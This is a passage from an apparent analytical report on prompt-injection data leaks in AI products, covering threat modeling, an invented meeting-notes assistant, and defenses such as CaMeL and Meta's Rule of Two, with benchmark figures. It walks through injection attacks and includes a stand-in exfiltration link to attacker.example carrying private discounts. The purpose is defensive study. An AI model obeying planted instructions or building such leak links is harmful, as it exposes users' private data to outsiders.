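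Without such a test, the best check is whether someone had already published a similar attack. By this standard, some of the early misses can reasonably be excused because the attacks were obvious only in hindsight. Few people had considered the picture leak when Samoilenko described it in spring 2023, and even Willison hadn't thought of link previews as a way to leak data until August 2024.

The defense is much weaker for later products. In December 2024, Willison (2024) was already adding xAI to a "growing list" of AI labs whose features could leak data through prompt injection. SearchLeak's prefilled link also had a precedent in Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface*, which described a ChatGPT address that filled in a prompt from its "q" parameter and submitted it without asking the user.

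Some companies foresaw the danger and released the feature anyway. Anthropic warned developers of a "residual risk" in Claude's page reader before Paul demonstrated the leak, and PromptArmor notes that Google dealt with Antigravity's known risks by including a disclaimer. The dispute in these cases is about whether the company should have accepted the risk.

Microsoft writes that the risk left in an AI system after sensible precautions is "not a failure of engineering". But it warns against dismissing severe harm as unlikely, because something that happens once in a million interactions may happen thousands of times a day in a large product. It also says a team should rethink a feature it can't defend without unacceptable harm to people. A disclaimer doesn't satisfy either warning very well, because it leaves the feature unchanged and relies on users to spot an attack designed to escape their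 notice. Rehberger considered the Antigravity flaws relatively simple to fix, which also makes it harder to justify releasing the program with them.

Published cases also leave out most of the flaws that reviewers caught. People outside the companies don't know how many there were, so they can't tell from the public record how often threat modeling fails. Bullwinkel and colleagues describe one success, in which their team found that a specially made video file could make an AI video service contact private parts of Microsoft's network, because the service used an outdated component. The service's developers updated the component and isolated it from the network.

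This was server-side request forgery, in which an outsider gets a company's server to send a request on their behalf. The Next Web uses the same term for the Bing relay in SearchLeak. Microsoft therefore had people who knew how to recognize and contain this kind of flaw. But the video service could work without network access, whereas Bing's image search has to contact outside websites.

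## How a review before launch could cover these features

A team can look for these flaws without guessing what an attacker will write. It needs a complete list of the product's features, and it has to treat the model's output as if a stranger had written it. Nobody appears to have tested the following four steps as a single procedure, but each would have pointed to a flaw in a real product.

1. List every feature that takes in text, stores it, displays it or sends a request. Include features older than the assistant and ones that run on another company's servers.
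2. Assume that the model may output anything, including any private text it has read.
3. Trace every path from text that an outsider could write to a request that leaves the product.
4. Ask who could do harm with each feature while using it exactly as the company offers it.

### An invented meeting-notes assistant

Suppose a company is about to launch an assistant that takes notes in video meetings. It posts the notes in the team's chat app, emails them to everyone on the invitation, and remembers what people are working on so that later notes make sense. If someone in the meeting asks for a document to go to a colleague, the assistant sends it.

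First, the team lists where text goes. Text reaches the model through speech, the meeting's chat, shared files and the calendar invitation. The product stores it in notes and memory, and displays it in the chat app and in email. Besides the emails the assistant sends, the chat app requests a page for each link preview, and a mail program may load pictures.

Testers can carry out the second step literally by replacing the model with a short program that returns the worst output they can think of. It might return a picture whose address contains a made-up secret, a link in an unusual format or a false note for memory. The testers then check whether the secret reaches their own web server. They don't have to trick a model, so the result won't change when the next model resists injection better or worse. They should record requests as well as read the finished answer, because in SearchLeak the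 browser sent its request before the filter cleaned up the text.

Checks in ordinary code also seem to hold up better than defenses that rely on the model. *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026) describes an automated attacker that adapted its attempts over hundreds of rounds. Every defense that relied on the model eventually failed, while a filter in the application's code let nothing through in 15,000 attacks. The test used a few planted secrets, though, which are probably easier for a filter to recognize than the confidential sentences in a real mailbox.

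For the third step, a reviewer could consider a salesperson's meeting with a customer who has hidden an instruction in the calendar invitation to end the notes with a reference link containing other customers' discounts. The assistant remembers those discounts from earlier meetings and posts the notes with a link to `attacker.example/ref?note=15`. The chat app's server requests that address to make a preview, which sends the discount to the customer even if nobody clicks the link.

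The trace also shows a simpler attack. The assistant emails the notes to everyone on the invitation, including the customer, so an instruction to mention the discounts in the notes would be enough to leak them. Restricting email to people at the meeting wouldn't help, because the attacker is one of them.

### Breaking the path

Willison advises removing one part of the lethal trifecta, and this has to be done for each path. Turning off previews stops the chat app from requesting the link, but the customer still gets the email.

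Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns a similar idea into a design rule. Until developers can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent that works without supervision should have no more than two of these properties in one session:

- **A:** It processes untrustworthy input.
- **B:** It has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** It changes something or communicates with the outside.

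Property C is broader than the trifecta's outside communication, so the rule also covers an agent that deletes an important message without sending anything. If a task needs all three properties, Meta calls for human approval of the agent's actions or another reliable check.

Meta gives the example of an email assistant that receives spam telling it to forward the user's inbox. Developers could let the assistant read only mail from trusted senders (removing A), run it without sensitive data (removing B), or let it write only to trusted recipients unless a person has checked the draft (limiting C). An agent's restrictions can also change partway through a task. It might browse the web without access to private data, then lose its outside connection before it opens internal systems.

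Meta gives no test results and acknowledges that a design can satisfy the rule and still fail, for example if a user blindly confirms a warning. Few testers refused the dangerous command in Anthropic's experiment, so this is a serious weakness in any design that depends on approval.

Memory also causes difficulty because Meta treats a session as new when the model starts with a fresh context, but saved notes can carry text over from earlier sessions. A sentence that a customer planted on Monday can return in an internal meeting on Thursday, when the team believes the assistant is reading nothing untrusted.

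In the invented product, the team could have the assistant write two sets of notes whenever a guest is present. The notes for colleagues may draw on memory, but they stay inside the company and contain no links or outside pictures. The notes for guests come from a separate session that has seen only that meeting. David C recommends a rule that leads to much the same design. The rule, from a discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista, is that when a model processes someone's text, its privileges should drop to that person's. The customer can't look up other customers' discounts, so the assistant shouldn't be able to while reading the customer's words.

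Applied strictly, that rule would also keep memory out of the colleagues' notes, so the two sets are a compromise. A hidden instruction could still distort what colleagues read, but leaking the discounts would be much harder.

### Choosing the actions before reading the text

Removing a whole property can make a product useless. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) describes six ways to limit what hostile text can affect while keeping more of the product's functions. They are based on the principle that once an agent has read untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger any harmful action.

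| Pattern | How it works | What hostile text can still do |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never reads the results | Nothing through the results |
| Plan, then execute | The model fixes its list of actions before reading outside text | Change the content of a planned email |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and gives a restricted answer, such as yes or no | Get its own document misclassified |
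| Dual LLM | One model plans and uses tools, while another reads outside text without tools | Change the text the second model returns |
| Code, then execute | The model writes a program that calls tools and passes outside text to a model without them | Change the data the program handles |
| Context minimization | The software removes the user's prompt before the model writes its answer | Influence the answer through retrieved data |

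Their email and calendar assistant resembles the invented one. When a user asks it to send today's schedule to a manager, then before it sees any appointments, it commits to reading the calendar and writing one email to that address. An instruction in an appointment can't add a recipient, but it can change what the email says. When the assistant is replying to the attacker's own email, hostile text could also make it hide private data in the reply as invisible characters.

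Beurer-Kellner and colleagues expect such an assistant to lose little by planning its actions before it reads text from strangers, because those actions should rarely depend on that text. They warn against exempting email to colleagues from the user's review, because an attacker may use such an email to get a colleague to approve something or ignore an alert. Microsoft's narrower exemption, for messages from Copilot Cowork to its own user, still let files leak.

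Google DeepMind's CaMeL develops the program-writing pattern furthest. It handles a request in four steps:

1. A privileged model reads the user's request and the descriptions of the tools, and writes a short program for the task.
2. A special interpreter runs the program. If the task involves understanding outside text, the interpreter gives that text to a quarantined model that has no tools.
3. The interpreter labels each piece of data with its origin and with who may read it. Anything made from that data inherits the labels.
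4. Before every tool call, the interpreter checks the labels against a security policy.

The program fixes which actions can happen and in what order, and the labels protect the data that passes through those actions. In an example from *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025), hostile text alters a recipient's address, and the policy can catch the change before the email goes out. *CaMeLoT* (2026), a proposal for extending the system, notes that such policies can block some unsafe actions even after an attacker has corrupted the model's plan. In the invented product, the discounts would carry a label restricting them to employees, so the interpreter would not email them to the customer. Someone still has to write that policy and label the discounts correctly.

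The protection can fail when several agents share a job. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, asked three CaMeL agents to send Julie a summary of job applicants on Slack. They had planted a request in the applicant database to send a copy to an outside address. The first two agents handled the request as data. The third received the summary as part of its instructions, treated the planted request as the user's, and emailed the outside address.

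Peters-Gill and colleagues propose passing instructions and data between agents through separate channels. In a simulated test with five models, fixed attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent, and never with the separate channels. Nearly all the successful attacks without CaMeL were against two older models, while GPT-5.5 resisted every attack even without it. The researchers left CaMeL's security policies empty, so a suitable policy might also have stopped the email to the outsider.

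### What the protection costs

Researchers often test these defenses on AgentDojo, a set of 97 simulated office, banking, chat and travel tasks with planted attacks. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) reports that CaMeL originally completed 77% of tasks under attack, compared with 84% for an unprotected agent. CaMeL also used about 2.8 times as many tokens, which makes each task more expensive. In a different test with several agents and no attacks, Peters-Gill and colleagues found that CaMeL reduced task success by 21.6 percentage points on average and by 13.4 points for the two strongest models.

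The drawback grows sharply when an assistant has to work out what to do as it goes. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) contains 60 tasks of this kind, in which the agent also has to follow some harmless outside instructions, such as a shop's request to log in before paying. Only six of AgentDojo's tasks require this sort of replanning. The table gives AgentDyn's results for GPT-4o.

| Defense | How it works | Tasks completed without an attack | Successful attacks |
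|---|---|---|---|
| None | | 53.3% | 37.8% |
| Spotlighting | Marks outside text as untrusted | 55.0% | 27.6% |
| PIGuard | Screens outside text for suspected instructions | 10.0% | 1.7% |
| Progent | Limits the tools available as the task proceeds | 6.7% | 1.7% |
| DRIFT | Plans first, then checks any change to the plan | 30.0% | 0.8% |
| CaMeL | Writes the whole program first | 0% | 0% |

No attacks succeeded against CaMeL, but that means little here because it also completed no tasks. Li and colleagues chose tasks that no fixed program could handle, so their result doesn't show how CaMeL would do in a product with more routine work. Writing notes and sending them to a known list takes the same steps every time, while the steps for carrying out follow-ups depend on what people mention.

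*AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) found that attacks succeeded far more often when the user didn't specify an action and the assistant decided what to do from the content it read. A notes assistant that acts on anything said in a meeting works this way by default. The team could instead have it list proposed follow-ups and let an employee choose which to carry out.

Agents that operate a computer screen are even harder to plan for. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) describes a CaMeL-style design that kept up to 57% of leading models' performance. A fake cookie notice inside an advertisement could still send the agent to a malicious site, because the plan already included dealing with cookie notices.

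Most of these security figures come from tests with fixed sets of attacks, and some defenses do much worse against attacks adapted to them. *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025) reports that attacks adapted to Spotlighting, a defense Microsoft uses, succeeded more than 95% of the time. PIGuard stopped every fixed attack on GPT-4o-mini, but when Ma and colleagues let a model revise the attacks, 28.0% succeeded. Of the five defenses that had done best against fixed attacks in that comparison, only Progent stayed effective against the revised attacks.

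Narisetty and colleagues also tried an adapted attack on Progent, using a small open model. It succeeded 2.6% of the time, compared with 4.2% for the fixed attacks, though they describe this as one small data point. Fixed limits on actions seem more resistant to attack than filters, but the evidence is limited.

Training can also help. *SecPO* (2026) reports cutting one adaptive attack's success rate on a small open model from 89.1% to 12.3% without making the model less useful.

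### Testing for open misuse

None of these defenses would have stopped people from using Tay's repetition game or Grok's image-edit button. In the fourth step, the team writes abuse cases, which describe what someone with bad intentions would do with a feature, as use cases describe what a customer would do. Trying them on the working product is sometimes called abusability testing.

Testers start with a goal, such as humiliating a stranger or making the company publish a slur, and may use only the product's own buttons and commands. They note how long it takes and how many people they could harm at once. A tester trying to get a slur published would probably have found Tay's repetition game within minutes. Testers also check whether the victim would find out, could refuse and could undo the damage. The image-edit button fails the first two of these checks, since X didn't tell people about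 edits or let them opt out.

ChatGPT's share checkbox needs a different test because its users meant no harm. The team could ask people, right after they tick the box, who can now read their chat. If many name only the friend they sent it to, the label isn't clear enough.

In the hypothetical product, a participant could wait until a colleague leaves the call and then say that the colleague agreed to pay for something, and the notes would record it as a decision. A manager could ask the assistant who complains most. Someone on a long invitation list who never attended would receive everything people said. None of these problems involves prompt injection, and a team could find them in an afternoon.

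Published measurements of how well misuse testing prevents attacks are hard to find. The argument for it rests mainly on past incidents where a simple trial could have revealed the problem. Still, the testing takes few resources and doesn't require rebuilding the product.

The next table puts the assistant through all four steps.

| Feature that the team lists | Worst output or use | Path or misuse | Planned default | Default after the review |
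|---|---|---|---|---|
| Link previews in team chat | A link containing private data | Guest's invitation to chat app's request | Previews on | Previews off, and no links in notes when a guest is present |
| Pictures in notes | A picture address containing private data | Guest's file to mail program's request | Outside pictures load | No outside pictures |
| Emailed notes | Other customers' discounts | Guest's invitation to guest's inbox | Same notes for everyone invited | Separate notes for guests, nothing automatic for absentees |
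| Memory | A false or hostile note | Guest's words to a later internal meeting | Saves from every meeting | Saves only from meetings without guests, after an employee sees the note |
| Follow-up tasks | A document sent to the wrong person | Anyone's words to an email | Acts on spoken requests | Lists requests for an employee to choose |
| Record of decisions | A false agreement | A participant, openly | States what "the team" decided | Names who said it |
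| Questions about colleagues | A ranking of complainers | A manager, openly | Answers from all saved notes | Answers about projects only |

The assistant still takes notes and sends them to the people who were there. Users lose previews and some automation, and the company pays for a second set of notes when guests attend. Some of the new defaults are stronger than others. A team can test whether previews are off, but an employee in a hurry may approve a bad follow-up without reading it.

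### What companies and public bodies ask for now

ChatGPT and Claude already limit which web addresses they open. OpenAI also offers stricter limits as an option.

OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced Lockdown Mode in February as an optional setting for organizations whose staff are likely targets, and OpenAI extended it to personal accounts from June. It turns off features including live web access, pictures in answers, agent mode, live connectors and file downloads. ChatGPT can then browse only saved copies of web pages, so no request leaves OpenAI's network. Administrators of business accounts can still allow particular apps and actions within them.

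This removes nearly all outside communication, and the list of disabled features shows how many channels ChatGPT normally has for it. OpenAI considers the mode unnecessary for most users. That may be reasonable for someone asking about recipes, but the people who most need the mode may not know it exists.

OpenAI's "Elevated Risk" label marks certain network features in ChatGPT, its Atlas browser and its coding agent Codex. In Codex, for example, the label appears where developers turn on internet access, with an explanation of what could go wrong. Like Google's disclaimer for Antigravity, the label does not block attacks. But OpenAI plans to remove each label once it considers the safeguards good enough, so the labels are in effect a public list of risks it has accepted for now.

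For companies that deploy agents, OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (August 2026) points out that a valid login doesn't establish which actions an agent may take. Security teams also need to verify whom the agent is acting for. The upload flaw in Claude Cowork involved this gap, since the attacker's key was valid but belonged to the wrong customer.

Government advice has become more specific. In May 2026, the Australian Cyber Security Centre published *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* jointly with cybersecurity agencies from the United States, Canada, New Zealand and Britain. The agencies recommend threat modeling with current lists of AI risks, safe defaults, and controls wherever information enters or leaves a system. A link preview is one such point, though the team could overlook it. They also say that designers or operators, not the agent, should decide when a person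 must approve an action. Antigravity's recommended settings left that decision to the agent. The agencies advise using agents only for low-risk, non-sensitive tasks, which would rule out most email assistants.

The agencies refer readers to OWASP and NIST. OWASP, a nonprofit that publishes lists of common software weaknesses, ranks prompt injection as the top risk for applications built on language models. NIST, the US standards institute, publishes guidance on "zero trust", in which a system checks each request instead of trusting requests from inside its own network. The Bing and Teams relays worked because Copilot trusted Microsoft's addresses.

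Britain's NCSC ties its advice to standards from ETSI, a European standards body. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *NCSC Publishes Guidance on Securing Agentic AI Use*, these include giving an agent the least access it needs, for the shortest time, and using temporary credentials. On August 20, 2026, after AI models had taken unintended actions in several incidents, the NCSC added interim advice about isolating agents and keeping people in control. Infosecurity Magazine's *NCSC Urges Stronger Controls for Agentic AI Systems* reports that formal guidance, still in preparation, would replace the interim advice.

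These documents are advisory. EU law imposes duties, but neither the "nudification" ban nor the Digital Services Act includes a method for checking a link preview or a memory feature for leaks.

### Keeping the review current

A review covers the product as it is on one day, but AI companies may change their products every week. Repeating the whole review after every change would be impractical, so the team needs to decide which changes call for a new trace. One such change is when a model starts writing text that only people used to write, as happened with links in chat apps. Others are when the product gets a new source of outside text, or when another company's product starts acting on the assistant's output, as Bankrbot did with Grok's posts.

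Developers can automatically test every new version against the hostile outputs from the second step. A saved test that posted a payment request from Grok's account would have shown Bankr that its rewritten software no longer blocked Grok.

Allow-lists need upkeep. The Australian Cyber Security Centre and its partners warn that incomplete or outdated lists can give agents unintended access. Each entry could have an owner, a reason and an expiry date. A tester should also check whether an ordinary outsider's account can receive a made-up secret at every permitted address. That test would probably have caught the problems with Google Forms in Superhuman and the upload service in Claude, which an expiry date would not have exposed.

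Tracing paths is quicker than examining every combination of features, but it can't find a feature that nobody listed. A team could easily leave out something like Microsoft's background processing of saved files. The agencies therefore recommend a phased release, in which an agent starts with little access and gains or loses it depending on the results of continued testing. The notes assistant might begin with internal meetings and admit guests later. A trial without attacks doesn't prove much, since a few hundred users are unlikely to attract a serious attacker. The company would also have to pay people to attack the assistant.

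Bounty programs can cover these features only if they accept reports of prompt injection. A company could pay for any demonstrated way to get private data out of the product, whether its staff would blame the model or the software. Google excluded Antigravity's known leaks from rewards. This is understandable, since no company wants to pay repeatedly for the same flaw, but it also discourages researchers from looking where the company already knows it is weak. A fair compromise might be to publish a repair date for each known issue and pay for new reports after that date.

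Every small feature also needs its own off switch. Superhuman could disable its vulnerable features on the first working day after PromptArmor's report, while Microsoft had to take Tay down completely. The company also has to log what the product refuses as well as what it does, so that it knows when to use the switch. David C notes that attackers usually have to refine an attack before it works, so a run of failed tool calls may be the first sign of an attack.
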